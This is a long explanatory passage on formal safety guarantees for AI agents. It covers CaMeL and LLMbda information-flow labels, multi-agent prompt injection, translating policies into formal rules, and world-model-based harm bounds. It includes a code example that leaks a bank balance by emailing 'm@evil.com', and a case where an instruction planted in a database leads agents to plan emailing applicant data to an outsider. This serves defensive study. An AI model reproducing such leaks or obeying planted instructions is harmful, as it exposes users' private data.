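FIDES's theorem covers one type of agent loop, and CaMeL has no comparable theorem. Garby and colleagues wanted a guarantee for any agent that a programmer might write. They started from the lambda calculus, a minimal programming language whose programs consist only of functions applied to one another, and added what agents need. The result is called LLMbda, and its additions are:

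- Conversations. A program can send a prompt to the model, receive the reply and clear the conversation. It can also *fork* the conversation, which means working in a temporary copy and then discarding it.
- Generated code. The model's reply can itself be a program, which the interpreter then runs.
- Labels. Every value and every conversation has one, and a program can require a particular label before it makes a sensitive call.
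- *Endorsement*. This command relabels an untrusted value as trusted.

CaMeL's two-model design can be written as a short program in this language. To read a complaint, the program forks the conversation, clears the copy, sends it the complaint and keeps only the reply, which is labelled untrusted. The main conversation never receives the complaint, so it can do the planning. The same theorem would also apply to an agent with five separate conversations, or to one that decides during a run what to isolate.

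Such a theorem is useful because labels are easy to get wrong. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter misses some implicit flows. A classic example, adapted to a bank's agent, looks like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Only the balance starts secret. If it is above the threshold, the third line sets *tmp* to False and labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so *rich* stays True and keeps its public label, and the interpreter allows the email. If the balance is below the threshold, *tmp* stays True and public, *rich* becomes False, and no email goes out. The email therefore reveals whether the balance exceeds the threshold, although the interpreter labels *rich* public in both cases.

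LLMbda stops a run if a secret would determine a change to a public conversation. An observer may notice that nothing happened, but this reveals at most one bit per run. CaMeL can leak more because it restarts failed plans from outside the interpreter, where no labels apply. An attacker could therefore compare a secret balance with a new threshold each time, and twenty answers would be enough to determine a balance of up to $1 million to the nearest dollar.

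### Why the guarantee is about probabilities

The definition of noninterference above assumes that the same input always leads to the same actions. But a language model picks its words at random, so two runs on the same input can differ. Garby and colleagues therefore compare the probabilities of the possible results. Ideally, each result would have the same probability under any two inputs that differ only in what the observer is not allowed to see.

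That ideal is out of reach because LLMbda enforces its labels by stopping runs, and hidden data can affect which runs it stops. The guarantee therefore has to be *termination-insensitive*, meaning that it allows hidden data to affect whether a run finishes. Suppose an agent produces these trusted results in response to two different complaints:

| | Refund | No refund | Run never finishes |
|---|---|---|---|
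| Complaint A | 0.5 | 0.3 | 0.2 |
| Complaint B | 0.6 | 0.2 | 0.2 |

For each result, we take the larger of the two probabilities, which gives 0.6 for a refund and 0.3 for no refund, or 0.9 in total. Because the total is at most 1, the two rows are *compatible*, meaning that both complaints could have had the same probability of a refund if more runs had finished. If complaint B led to a refund with probability 0.8, the total would be 0.8 + 0.3 = 1.1. Unfinished runs could not explain the difference between the complaints in that case, so the complaint must have influenced the refund.

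The theorem is that the results are compatible for every LLMbda program and every such pair of inputs. If all runs finish, compatible probabilities are equal, which gives ordinary noninterference. Otherwise, the distance between the two sets of probabilities (half the sum of their absolute differences) is at most the average probability that a run doesn't finish. In the table, the distance is 0.1 and the limit is 0.2.

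To prove the theorem, Garby and colleagues use a simplified run that skips any computation as soon as its label exceeds what the observer may see, and substitutes an empty value. The simplified run never reads the hidden data, so its probabilities are the same for both inputs. It also produces each visible result at least as often as the real runs do. Its probabilities are therefore at least as large as those in both rows and add up to at most 1, as compatibility requires.

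The proofs are written in Lean, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. The interpreter that calls the language model is also a Lean program, and another theorem shows that its results have the probabilities the theory assigns to them. The guarantees still depend on trusting Lean, the code that contacts the model over the internet, and the assumption that the model's replies follow fixed probabilities. Garby and colleagues also treat all tools and data sources as part of the program, so the proof would not cover a real shop's database and mail server.

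To test the language, they wrote an agent that practises each plan on simulated data before running it for real. On the banking tasks, it completed 75% of runs with GPT-5.2 and 65% with MiMo-v2.5, about twice CaMeL's rate when CaMeL enforces its policies. Only 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. But there are only 16 banking tasks, and the new agent enforces only some of CaMeL's policies. It can also endorse untrusted data. Without endorsement, its completion rate with MiMo-v2.5 fell to 54%. In two thirds of the combinations of task and attack, planning in advance would be enough to stop the attack, because the plan would never contain the calls the attacker needs.

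### When agents instruct other agents

Labels can also get lost between agents. The shop might use one agent for complaints and another for sending messages, and the second might treat requests from the first as trusted. Peters-Gill and colleagues built such a system, with every agent using CaMeL, and asked it to send a coworker a summary of job applicants on Slack. They had hidden an instruction in the applicant database to email the data to an outsider. The coordinating agent included the summary, with that instruction, in its request to the messaging agent, whose planner treated the request as trusted and added the email to its plan.

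The multi-CaMeL paper proves that any system of two or more agents arranged in a tree has this weakness if one of its tools returns untrusted data and the agents can freely pass on results. The paper's remedy, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data through separate channels. Its interpreter refuses any instruction that depends on a tool's output.

In a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, the average success rate of attacks was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and zero with multi-CaMeL. GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks even without CaMeL. The formula for clean records then gives an upper bound of about 0.3% on the success rate of similar attacks, but it gives no bound for attackers who adapt to the model. Peters-Gill and colleagues cite a large public competition in which attackers succeeded against every leading model tested.

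One of them, Ilia Shumailov, also helped design CaMeL. In their paper, the researchers respond to Garby and colleagues' criticisms. They accept that CaMeL's interpreter misses some implicit flows and say that multi-CaMeL has the same fault, which still needs fixing. The leak through repeated attempts doesn't affect multi-CaMeL, because it never retries a failed plan.

### Errors that correct tracking allows

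Even a perfect interpreter relies on people to label the original data correctly. Costa and colleagues treat an email's sender and recipients as its readers, although somebody may have shared it more widely. For AgentDojo, they labelled a type of data as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. This gives a clear baseline, but a shop can't know in advance which fields an attacker will choose. If the shop trusts a "delivery notes" field that customers can edit, the planner will read whatever they write there.

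People can also approve flows they should refuse. Costa and colleagues warn that asking employees too often to approve blocked calls tires them out and gives attackers a chance to trick them. If an employee accepts the fraudster's address as Ann's, the software will treat it as trusted from then on. Endorsement in LLMbda leaves a similar decision to the planner, which at least makes it before receiving any untrusted data. Garby and colleagues also prove that endorsement can't weaken the secrecy guarantee. Endorsing too much could therefore send money to the wrong person, but it couldn't reveal Ann's record.

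Harmful content can also pass through the agent as ordinary text. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that tells the isolated model to produce an empty summary. The agent makes no forbidden call, but the user gets a useless answer. Their rules also let the text of some messages depend on untrusted data, because an agent that couldn't pass on what it had read would be little use. A false claim in a customer's complaint could therefore reach the summary that an employee reads before deciding on a refund.

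The hardest cases are tasks in which untrusted data has to determine the plan. Costa and colleagues put 44% of AgentDojo's banking tasks and 43% of its Slack tasks in this category, but at most 10% in the other two settings. One banking task asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on this task without policies, the planner sometimes wrote a program that could carry out whatever calls the file requested, which gave untrusted text the control that CaMeL is supposed to prevent.

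In both successful attacks on the LLMbda agent, the user asked it to make a payment described in a file whose contents the attacker had replaced. CaMeL's designers regard this case as outside their threat model. Without endorsement, LLMbda blocks the attack, but it also blocks the payment when the file is genuine. Real and forged bills arrive by the same route and carry the same labels, so the agent needs other evidence to tell them apart, such as a list of approved suppliers.

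## Turning written requirements into formal rules

Agent-C, Cedar and CaMeL enforce rules that are already precise, such as "at most $200". Managers rarely write policies that way. The shop's handbook might say, "Refund loyal customers promptly unless something looks wrong." A new employee could follow this, but no program can check it until someone defines "loyal", "promptly" and "looks wrong".

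### What one sentence leaves open

The harness has to start recording the arrival of complaints and the passing of days before any rule can cover "promptly", because neither is a tool call.

Each term also needs a definition. "Loyal" could mean an account older than two years, five past orders or the Platinum tier. "Promptly" could mean an hour, a day or a week. "Something looks wrong" is the hardest to define, because a monitor can only test recorded facts. The shop might use a warning from fraud-detection software, a recent change of address or a button that employees press when they suspect a problem.

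Suppose the shop settles on accounts older than two years, 24 hours and a flag set by the fraud software. One possible rule is

G((complaint ∧ loyal ∧ ¬flag) → F≤24h refund)

Whenever a loyal customer without a flag complains, a refund must follow within 24 hours. The deadline makes this a safety property, since a finite trace can show that 24 hours passed without a refund. But a monitor that only blocks calls can't make the agent issue the refund, so the harness would have to alert an employee before the deadline.

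In this formula, a flag merely removes the duty to pay, and the agent may still refund a flagged customer. The manager may have meant that it must not:

G(refund → ¬flag)

If the agent refunds $40 to a flagged customer, it satisfies the first rule and violates the second. Adopting both rules can create a conflict. If a loyal customer complains at 9:00 and the software flags her at 11:00, before she gets a refund, the first rule still requires the refund and the second forbids it while the flag remains.

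The handbook also doesn't mention new customers, so a word-for-word translation into Cedar, which refuses by default, would give them nothing. Even leaving new customers aside, three definitions for each of three phrases and two readings of "unless" produce 54 different rules.

All 54 are *well formed*, meaning they follow the grammar of the formal language and refer to things that exist. As with Cedar, software can check this but can't determine which of the 54 the manager meant. Suppose someone defines "loyal" as "account age above 730", thinking of days, but the database stores months. Nobody has had an account for 60 years, so the rule never requires a refund, and a proof that the agent follows it will succeed.

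### A review of the evidence

Language models can now translate written requirements into formal rules, and Dantas and colleagues regard this step as the bottleneck for the whole field. For their systematic review, they searched six databases in May 2026 for work on specifying, verifying and enforcing rules for agents. They screened 71 records, read 47 papers in full and kept 38, only eight of which deal mainly with specification. Their main finding on translation is that language models got between 24.8% and 34.2% of planning tasks right on one benchmark.

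Dantas and colleagues rated the evidence with GRADE, a system from medicine. In their version, each claim starts at High and drops one level for each of four problems: weak methods, conflicting results, a setting unlike real use, and too little data. The translation claim drops three levels and is one of the seven rated Very Low.

The other two claims are rated Moderate: no agent scored above 60% on a large safety benchmark, and more than 90% of translations into temporal logic are well formed. The evidence that models can write well-formed rules is therefore stronger than the evidence about whether those rules are right.

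The review has its own weaknesses. One person selected the studies. When three of the authors later screened 37 records from a repeated search, they agreed on most but found 11 relevant papers the review had missed. They also judged three of the 38 studies to be outside the review's scope, and the Moderate rating for well-formed translations relies largely on those three.

### Where the percentages come from

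Both percentages come from *Planetarium* (Zuo, Piedrahita Velez and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark that predates the review by two years. It tested GPT-4o, o1-mini and three sizes of Gemma 2 on translating English into PDDL, a language for planning problems. A PDDL problem has two files. The domain file lists the possible actions, with their preconditions and effects, and the problem file gives the objects, the starting state and the goal. The models received the domain file and an English description, and wrote only the problem file.

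The tasks involve stacking blocks, moving balls between rooms and painting floor tiles. The researchers used templates to generate 145,918 pairs of descriptions and correct files, and kept about 16,000 for testing. Some descriptions list every fact, such as which block is on which. Others give a summary, such as that all the blocks should be in a single tower.

The same goal can be written in many ways, so comparing a model's file with the correct one word for word would be too strict. In a world with only two blocks, "block 1 is on block 2" implies that block 2 is on the table and that the robot's hand is empty, so a file that also lists those facts describes the same goal. Zuo and colleagues' program therefore adds all implied facts to both files, turns each file into a graph, and checks whether the objects can be paired up so that the graphs are identical. They prove that this test succeeds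 exactly when the two files describe equivalent problems.

A PDDL parser could read 96.1% of GPT-4o's files, and 94.4% described a solvable problem, but only 24.8% described the right problem. In about 70% of cases, a planner could have produced a valid plan for the wrong task.

The 34.2% is the score of the largest Gemma model after additional training, so the two percentages describe two particular models and aren't a range for language models in general. Many errors also had little to do with the task. The models kept assigning types to objects in domains that don't use types, and accuracy rose sharply when Zuo and colleagues ignored these type assignments.

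### Results with newer models

In February 2025, most models still struggled, according to *An Extensive Evaluation of PDDL Capabilities in off-the-shelf LLMs* (2025), which used more than 13,000 of the Planetarium pairs. The best models of 2026 do far better. In *Grounded Evaluation and Repair for NL-to-PDDL Problem Generation*, Rosa, Santos and colleagues (2026) ran three models on about 60 Planetarium problems with the same equivalence test. After a failed check, the model received feedback and could try again, up to twice. The researchers also wrote 60 harder problems involving durations or numerical quantities.

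| Model | Planetarium: correct at first attempt | Planetarium: correct after repair | Harder problems: passed all checks | Harder problems: matched the reference file |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1-mini | 18.3% | 26.7% | 50.0% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 93.2% | 93.2% | 98.3% | 6.7% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 96.7% | 100% | 93.3% | 25.0% |

The review's percentages therefore no longer describe the best systems on this benchmark. But the new sample is small. By the formula for clean test records, the error rate could still be as high as about 5% after 60 correct answers out of 60. Planetarium has also been public since 2024, so its problems may be in the training data of newer models.

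The last two columns are harder to interpret. To pass all checks, a file had to be readable, fit the domain and lead to a valid plan, and another language model had to accept it as faithful to the description. Nearly all of GPT-5.5's files passed, yet few matched the reference. Rosa and colleagues had no test of equivalence for these problems, so they could only compare the files fact by fact, allowing for renamed objects. Some mismatches may be harmless differences in style, but others are mistakes, such as leaving out the quantity the plan should minimise.

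Templated text is also tidier than what people write. Balyo, Chrpa and Youngblood (2026), in *Which LLM is Best for Translating Natural Language Goals to PDDL*, collected 90 informal goals from employees of their company, which tests video games with planning software. More than half came from people who had never used PDDL. Six models from 2025 each handled 92% to 96% of the goals correctly.

Half of these goals were impossible to express in the given domain, and the right response was to say so. Each model still wrote a formal goal for two to four of the 45 impossible ones. This kind of error is a particular concern for the shop. If its database has no field for suspicious behaviour, a model might translate "something looks wrong" as "the order number is missing", and the resulting rule would pass every check for form. The models made many more such errors before Balyo and colleagues expanded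 the prompt with a list of reasons why a goal might be inexpressible.

In all these tests, somebody had already written the domain file. For the shop, the equivalent would be deciding beforehand which events the harness records and what counts as a flag, which is much of the difficulty in formalising the handbook's sentence. *PDDLCoder* (2026) describes a harder benchmark in which the model must also work out the actions' preconditions and effects.

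### Finding out whether a rule is right

No program can compare a rule with what its author had in mind, but a manager who can't read temporal logic can still judge a concrete case. A solver could search for a run that the draft rule allows and present it as a question: "A customer of three years has a fraud flag and receives $40. Is that all right?" If the manager says no, the rule is wrong. There is little direct evidence that showing people such counterexamples helps. Dantas and colleagues cite a study of 12 users in which automated checking improved the quality of their plans and their satisfaction, but the study didn't cover rules.

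Before writing a formula, software can also prompt the requirement's author to clarify ambiguous phrases. Dantas and colleagues report that one such tool, NL2Spec (2023), translated requirements into temporal logic correctly in 44.4% to 86.1% of cases, depending on how the ambiguities were resolved.

To find the ambiguities, the shop could have a model translate the policy several times and compare the results. For two candidate rules A and B, a solver looks for a run that satisfies

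(A ∧ ¬B) ∨ (¬A ∧ B)

Any solution is a case that the two rules treat differently. For the two readings of "unless", one solution could be a $40 refund to a flagged customer, and the manager would only have to decide that case. If there is no solution, the rules are equivalent, but they may both be wrong. The models in Planetarium repeatedly added types to untyped objects, and comparing translations would not reveal a mistake they all shared. Dantas and colleagues list this kind of comparison as a direction for future research.

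Another remedy is to translate the rule back into plain language. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) splits a policy into numbered requirements and links each one to the rules that implement it, which exposes any requirement or rule that has no counterpart. A model then describes each rule in English without seeing the original text, so that it cannot simply repeat the policy. A reader can easily spot a mistake in a description such as "customers with accounts older than 730 months".

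Someone still has to compare the description with the policy, and a language model may not do this reliably. Rosa and colleagues checked 24 verdicts by the model that judged faithfulness in their tests and agreed with 13, little better than chance. The model rejected eight faithful translations and accepted three unfaithful ones. Their main experiments used GPT-4.1-mini as the judge, so a stronger model might do better.

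The shop could also infer rules from its records, as Greenlight does in part. Dantas and colleagues call this approach nascent. However, many rules can fit the same records. If every past refund was below $80, the records are consistent with a limit of $80, a limit of $200 or no limit. *VIGIL* (2026) uses records more cautiously. A model translates the written policy, but it may use only terms that appear in the policy, a recorded run or the rule language. It must output "Unsupported" if it can't express a rule in those terms. This guards against invented facts, though a rule made entirely of real terms can still be wrong.

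### Narrow rules or complete ones

Researchers disagree about how far these methods can go. Dantas and colleagues stress that new domains have no independent standard for checking a translation, and they found no study with an error rate below 10% for open-ended tasks. If the translated rule is wrong, a verifier may report that a harmful plan is safe. It may also block legitimate steps, which adds to the verifier tax.

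Others aim only to enforce a few clear rules for a particular task. In *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026) describe a study by Hong and colleagues of an agent that works with medical records. Hong and colleagues wrote code to enforce 23 of the 88 rules in their policy, leaving the other 65 unenforced. Without the code, the agent broke at least one of the 23 rules in 23% of ordinary runs and 62% of runs with adversarial prompts. With it, the agent broke none of them in either kind of run.

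Mondl and colleagues at the security company Sondera tried to cover more of the policy automatically. Gemini 3 Pro translated the policy into Cedar rules. Software checked the rules' form, and another model judged their meaning. The team also had Claude Opus 4.7 copy further restrictions from Hong and colleagues' code. When they applied the resulting rules to recorded runs, the rules blocked 85 of the 86 ordinary runs in which the agent had tried to change a medical record despite the 23 hand-coded rules.

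Mondl and colleagues present this as evidence of broader coverage, but it could equally be evidence that the rules are too strict. The tasks were legitimate, and a single rule against changing any record would have blocked all 86. Two of the rules that blocked calls most often required the agent to restate the patient's identity and to get confirmation before a change. The agent can't respond to a refusal by asking for confirmation in a recorded run, so the test doesn't measure how much work it could have done under these rules. The researchers warn that overly narrow policies lead developers to switch protections off.

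AWS sells a product called Automated Reasoning checks, which uses logic to reduce false statements by AI systems in areas with clearly defined rules. Crouse (2025), in *Amazon's Mitigating AI Hallucinations Through This Mathematical Method*, reports that the method works best where the data follow strict rules, such as important company policies. The article relays AWS's claims about the method but gives no measurement of its accuracy. Such a check depends on its premises being true. In Amazon's example, cats are mammals and mammals live on land, so cats live on land. The reasoning is valid and the conclusion is fine for most cats, but not all mammals live on land, and the same premise would let the software confirm that whales live on land.

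The case for narrow rules is strongest when a rule limits the damage without having to define what is suspicious. If the shop pays at most one refund per order and at most $200 each time, wrong refunds on 1,000 orders can't cost more than $200,000, whatever "looks wrong" means. For flagged complaints, the shop can require an event that software is able to check:

G((refund ∧ flag) → approved)

Here "approved" means that an employee has approved this refund. The rule leaves the judgement to the employee and guarantees only that the agent can't skip the approval. It doesn't stop a fraudster whom the software fails to flag, or an insulting email that no rule mentions. The problem is harder for agents that control machines, because a rule against injuring people needs a model of how the machine's movements affect them.

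## Bounding the probability of harm with a model of the world

The harness can enforce the $200 limit without information about customers, because the limit applies only to the refund request. A limit on injuries, blackouts or fraud losses concerns what happens after the agent acts, so proving that it holds requires a mathematical description of the agent's surroundings. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) propose writing that description and proving bounds relative to it. They call the result *guaranteed safe AI*. The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) is funding the idea through its Safeguarded AI programme, which Dalrymple directed at first. ARIA's *Funded projects* gives the programme's budget as £59 million.

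### World model, specification and verifier

The proposal adds three components to an AI system. The world model describes how the system's actions affect its surroundings, including what the modellers are unsure of. The specification states which effects are acceptable. The verifier shows, with a proof or a bound on a probability, that the system meets the specification if the world model is right. For the shop, the world model would describe how often fraudsters write in and how customers react to refunds. The specification could be that fraud losses stay below $10,000 a month with 99% probability.

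Dalrymple and colleagues rank versions of each component by how much safety they would provide if they worked. The table gives three examples for each component.

| Component | Weak version | Stronger version | Very ambitious version |
|---|---|---|---|
| World model | A trained simulator that nobody can interpret | Causal models that human experts have fully audited | Models proved to be faithful simplifications of physics |
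| Specification | The intuitions of human judges | Hand-written rules for a few properties | Everything that people might want, in all contexts |
| Verifier | Improvised tests | Tests that would cover every input if they ran forever | A proven upper limit on the probability of failure |

The highest level for world models uses no model and requires a proof that the specification holds in every possible world. The shop's proof that only customers in *Verified* receive refunds comes close to this, since it holds however customers behave. A limit on fraud losses can't be proved this way, because in some possible worlds every customer is a fraudster.

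Dalrymple and colleagues accept that nobody can predict people in detail. They suggest giving the verifier a set of possible behaviours for each person and requiring the specification to hold for every behaviour in the set. A larger set is more likely to include what people actually do, but it makes the proof harder.

One argument against relying on tests is that the world can change after testing. A self-driving car might cover a million miles without trouble before human drivers start driving more aggressively around such cars. Another argument comes from the history of bridges. About a quarter of those built in the 1870s collapsed within a decade, and deeper engineering theory later brought the rate below 0.4% per decade.

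One might instead try to understand the AI system well enough to prove things about it directly. Dalrymple and colleagues think a model of the world may often be simpler than the AI system, just as the rules of chess are simpler than a strategy for playing it well, but they regard this as an open empirical question.

Somebody also has to choose the 99% figure. Under the proposal, society would ideally set acceptable risks by collective deliberation. ARIA's older programme page, *Safeguarded AI*, lists six teams working on these social and legal questions. One, at the University of Warwick, studies how to combine different people's preferences about safety.

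### The gatekeeper

Dalrymple (2024) calls the whole arrangement a *gatekeeper* in *Safeguarded AI*, the programme's original thesis. Like Agent-C, a gatekeeper would keep an agent within agreed limits, but the limits would cover the consequences of the agent's actions as well as its tool calls.

Some powerful AI models would help experts write the world model and the specification. Others would search for proofs, which a separate, formally verified program would check. A training process would then turn a large model into a smaller network that is easier to verify. People would audit the world model, because every proof depends on it.

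Dalrymple wanted a guarantee that covers an infinite family of plausible starting conditions, not just the cases someone thought to test. The programme was to demonstrate such a guarantee in at least one narrow field, such as balancing an electricity grid or managing a supply chain.

The thesis also had a political aim. Dalrymple argued that countries and companies might agree to use very powerful AI only inside such systems if the research took less than 15 years and the systems delivered more than 5% of the economic value of unrestricted AI along the way. These thresholds come from a simplified game-theoretic model, so they are more illustrations of the argument than forecasts.

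### Harm compared with doing nothing

A grid can fail in a storm whatever its controller does, so an absolute limit on the probability of blackouts would count some that the controller could not have prevented. The programme's second thesis, Ammann's *Safeguarded AI* of May 2026, suggests capping the risk of harm relative to a counterfactual in which the system does nothing. This relative risk comes from causal inference, and formal verification would prove that it stays under the cap.

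Suppose the probability of a blackout this winter is 3% if the AI controller runs the grid and 2.5% if it does nothing. Comparing the two interventions shows that running the grid adds 0.5 percentage points to the probability of a blackout.

The probability that a blackout happens with the controller and would not have happened without it could be anything from 0.5% to 3%. At the lower end, the controller never prevents a blackout and causes a few extra ones. At the upper end, it prevents every blackout that would have happened without it and causes every one that does happen. As with the customer who received a refund and stayed, no experiment can distinguish these cases. A structural causal model can, but then the bound depends on equations that data alone can't confirm.

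A formal definition of harm must also specify the baseline before verification can start. "Doing nothing" might mean freezing the grid's settings or handing control to human operators, and the same controller could look dangerous compared with one and helpful compared with the other. Doing nothing can also be harmful, as when a refund agent leaves honest customers without their money.

### A certificate for a 2% bound

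A *supermartingale certificate* can bound the probability that something bad ever happens. It is a function that gives a number to every state of the world model and meets three conditions:

- The number is never negative.
- From any state, the expected number after the next step is no higher than the current one.
- The number is at least 1 in every unsafe state.

The probability of ever reaching an unsafe state is then at most the number at the start.

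Suppose thieves have taken over one of the shop's customer accounts. At each step, either the shop's agent recovers a stolen account or the thieves take over another. According to the world model, the agent recovers an account with a probability of at least 1/2, whatever the thieves do. The incident ends when no stolen accounts remain. The shop wants to know how likely it is that the number of stolen accounts ever reaches 50.

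Let x be the number of stolen accounts, and try V(x) = x/50. It is never negative, and it equals 1 when x is 50. If the agent succeeds with probability exactly 1/2, the expected value after one step is

½ · (x + 1)/50 + ½ · (x − 1)/50 = x/50,

and a more successful agent makes it lower. All three conditions hold. The incident starts with one stolen account, and V(1) = 0.02, so the probability of ever reaching 50 is at most 2%.

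To see why, imagine a large number of such incidents, and freeze each one if it reaches 50. The average of V starts at 0.02 and can't rise. V is 1 for each incident that has reached 50 and at least 0 for the others, so if more than 2% had reached 50, the average would be above 0.02. This argument works after any number of steps, so it covers the whole future. When the agent's chance is exactly 1/2, the true probability is exactly 2%, so no certificate could give a smaller bound.

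Certificates are attractive because checking this doesn't require simulating the thieves. A simple fraction won't work as V for a power grid controlled by a neural network, so Ammann's thesis proposes training a second network as V. Checking a certificate should take far less work than finding one, so the shop or the grid operator could let an untrusted AI do the search and trust only a small checker. But the checker has to confirm the conditions in every state, which for a trained certificate means verifying a neural network.

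### What a small modelling error does

The 2% holds in the world model. If real thieves are better than the model assumes, the real probability may be higher.

We can measure the error at one step by the *total variation distance*, the largest difference between the probabilities that the model and reality assign to any event. Suppose it is never more than 0.0001. We can then imagine the model and reality running side by side, with the same luck as far as possible, so that they separate at each step with a probability of at most 0.0001. Over 1,000 steps, the probability that they separate at some point is at most

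1,000 × 0.0001 = 0.1.

The bound for those 1,000 steps therefore rises from 2% to 12%. In a similar example, Dalrymple and colleagues use a slightly sharper formula, 1 − (1 − ε)^n, which gives 9.5% instead of 10%. Errors may cancel out in practice, but the bound must hold in the worst case. After 10,000 steps, the simple sum reaches 1, so it no longer provides any guarantee.

The shop could limit the error's effect by deploying the agent for a shorter time. Over 100 steps, the error adds at most one percentage point to the probability of harm. But if the shop renews the deployment without correcting the model, the error can again add up to ten percentage points over ten deployments. Dalrymple and colleagues recommend both limited deployments and a monitor that compares events with the world model, with a backup system ready to take over if they don't match.

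It would also take a lot of data to show that the error is as small as 0.0001. Suppose the only possible error is an event that the model rules out, such as thieves taking over two accounts at once. By the formula for clean test records, the shop would need about 30,000 steps without such an event to support an upper bound of 0.0001. The shop now has to bound rare errors in the world model instead of rare failures of the agent. That may still be progress, because several agents can share one world model, and the shop need not collect new data for each. But the data lose their value if thieves change their methods.

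### Learning the world model from data

*Can a Bayesian Oracle Prevent Harm from an Agent?* (Bengio, Cohen and colleagues, 2024) avoids committing to a single world model. Bengio also contributed to the earlier *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*. He and three of his co-authors on the Bayesian oracle paper belong to LawZero, a research organisation in Montréal.

The method starts from a list of theories. Each theory gives probabilities for what the system will observe and for whether an action will cause harm. Each also has a *prior weight*, its plausibility before any data arrive. After each observation, the method multiplies each theory's weight by the probability the theory gave to that observation, then rescales the weights to add up to 1. The rescaled weights are the theories' *posterior weights*.

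Averaging the theories' predictions according to these weights could underestimate the probability of harm, because the true theory may have a low weight and so contribute little to the average. Bengio and colleagues therefore look for a pessimistic but still plausible theory and use its prediction as an upper bound.

Bengio and colleagues first assume that the observations are independent draws from one fixed distribution. If the true theory is on the list with nonzero prior weight and no two theories are identical, its posterior weight tends to 1 as observations accumulate. They multiply each theory's posterior weight by the probability of harm it predicts, and prove that with enough observations, the theory with the largest product predicts at least as high a probability of harm as the true theory does. The theorem doesn't specify how many observations are enough.

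An agent that learns as it acts affects the data it learns from, so its observations are not independent draws. The true theory may then never dominate the posterior, but its weight is unlikely to become negligible. If its prior weight is p, then with probability at least 1 − δ its posterior weight never falls below δp.

The proof uses another certificate, δp/w, where w is the current weight of the true theory. This number is never negative, and Bengio and colleagues show that it doesn't rise in expectation. It starts at δ, because w starts at p, and it reaches 1 exactly when w has fallen to δp. The probability that this ever happens is therefore at most δ.

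This leads to the main bound, which uses a set of theories selected from a ranking by posterior weight. A theory belongs to the set if its weight is at least a fraction α of the combined weight of itself and all the theories above it. If α is less than δp, the true theory stays in the set at all times with probability at least 1 − δ. As long as it does, the highest probability of harm under any theory in the set is an upper bound on the true probability of harm.

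### One action under three theories

Suppose the shop receives hundreds of similar complaints about broken kettles, and its agent proposes to refund all the customers at once. The shop counts a large fraud loss as harm and considers three theories.

| Theory | Posterior weight | Probability of harm | Product |
|---|---|---|---|
| The factory shipped a faulty batch | 0.90 | 0.001 | 0.0009 |
| Some customers are copying a story they read online | 0.09 | 0.05 | 0.0045 |
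| A criminal gang wrote the complaints | 0.01 | 0.9 | 0.0090 |

The products add up to 0.0144, which is the average prediction. If the shop uses this average and blocks any action with more than a 2% chance of harm, it will allow the refunds. The method for independent data gives a bound of 0.9 because the gang theory has the largest product, so a shop using that bound will block the refunds. Refunding everyone would be a disaster if the gang theory is true, but blocking the refunds would deny them to hundreds of honest customers if the factory is to blame.

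The main bound depends sharply on how much confidence the shop wants. Suppose each theory had a prior weight of 1/3. For 95% confidence, α must be below 0.05 × 1/3, or about 0.0167. The shop can choose 0.016, which excludes the gang theory and gives a bound of 0.05. For 97% confidence, α must be below 0.01, which no longer excludes the gang theory, and the bound rises to 0.9.

### The exploding slot machine

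Bengio and colleagues tested their bounds on a simulated slot machine with ten arms. The agent can see which of ten features each arm has, but not which features pay. The reward is the number of paying features on the chosen arm plus random noise, and the machine explodes if the reward exceeds a threshold, so the agent's goal conflicts with its safety. An episode lasts up to 25 steps, and the researchers ran 10,000 episodes for each setting.

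The experiment compared *guardrails*, programs that forbid an action if its estimated probability of harm is above a limit. With α close to 0, the guardrail based on the main bound rejected almost every action, so there were few explosions and little reward. With α close to 1, it rejected few actions and the machine often exploded. At values in between, it performed much like a guardrail that used the average prediction, sometimes better and sometimes worse.

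The theorem's guarantee applies mainly to small values of α, which give more cautious bounds. There are 2^10 = 1,024 possible hidden lists with equal prior weight, so 95% confidence requires α to be below about 0.00005. For larger values, the bound was still correct more often than the theorem guarantees. But for actions with a true probability of harm of 50%, a large α usually produced an underestimate. The good overall record came from less dangerous actions.

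A limit on the risk of each action also lets the total risk grow over many actions, as with the shop's 1,000 actions. If each of 25 steps has a 10% chance of causing an explosion, the chance of at least one explosion is 93%.

The slot machine example involves few enough theories for a computer to update the weight of each one. A model of customers or a power grid would involve far too many, so Bengio and colleagues suggest training a neural network to estimate the weights. The network would make errors, and an agent might learn to propose actions whose danger the network underestimates. They list this as an open problem, along with the risk of blocking too many actions.

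Relying on records of harm causes another difficulty. While the records are accurate, the theory that a fraud happened and the theory that somebody recorded a fraud make the same predictions, so no amount of data can distinguish them. Their predictions would differ if an agent altered the records. Bengio and colleagues propose keeping both theories in the set and treating interference with the records as harm, so that the system tries to avoid the first such act.

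All these bounds require the true theory to be on the list. Bengio and colleagues mention that partial theories, such as the stories people tell about what could go wrong, might relax this requirement, but leave this to future work.

### Dickson's objections

Dickson (2024), in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, doubts that anyone will write a good enough world model in the near future. His first example is the spacecraft that landed the Perseverance rover on Mars in 2021. Engineers formally verified its software but proved nothing about the landing itself. According to an analysis that Dickson cites, software accounts for about 20% of the risk of failure in Mars missions, so perfect software would still leave the other 80%.

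Dickson then considers an example from *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, a machine that makes DNA to order and keeps the risk of harm below a set limit. He argues that predicting how a new virus affects people would require simulating a whole human body for years. In 2022, researchers simulated 20 minutes in the life of one unusually simple cell; a human body has about 36 trillion. The simulation would also need data on its starting state. Google scientists' map of about a millionth of a human brain took up 1.4 petabytes. The talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* makes the same objection more bluntly, comparing the request to "a thousand years of progress in microbiology".

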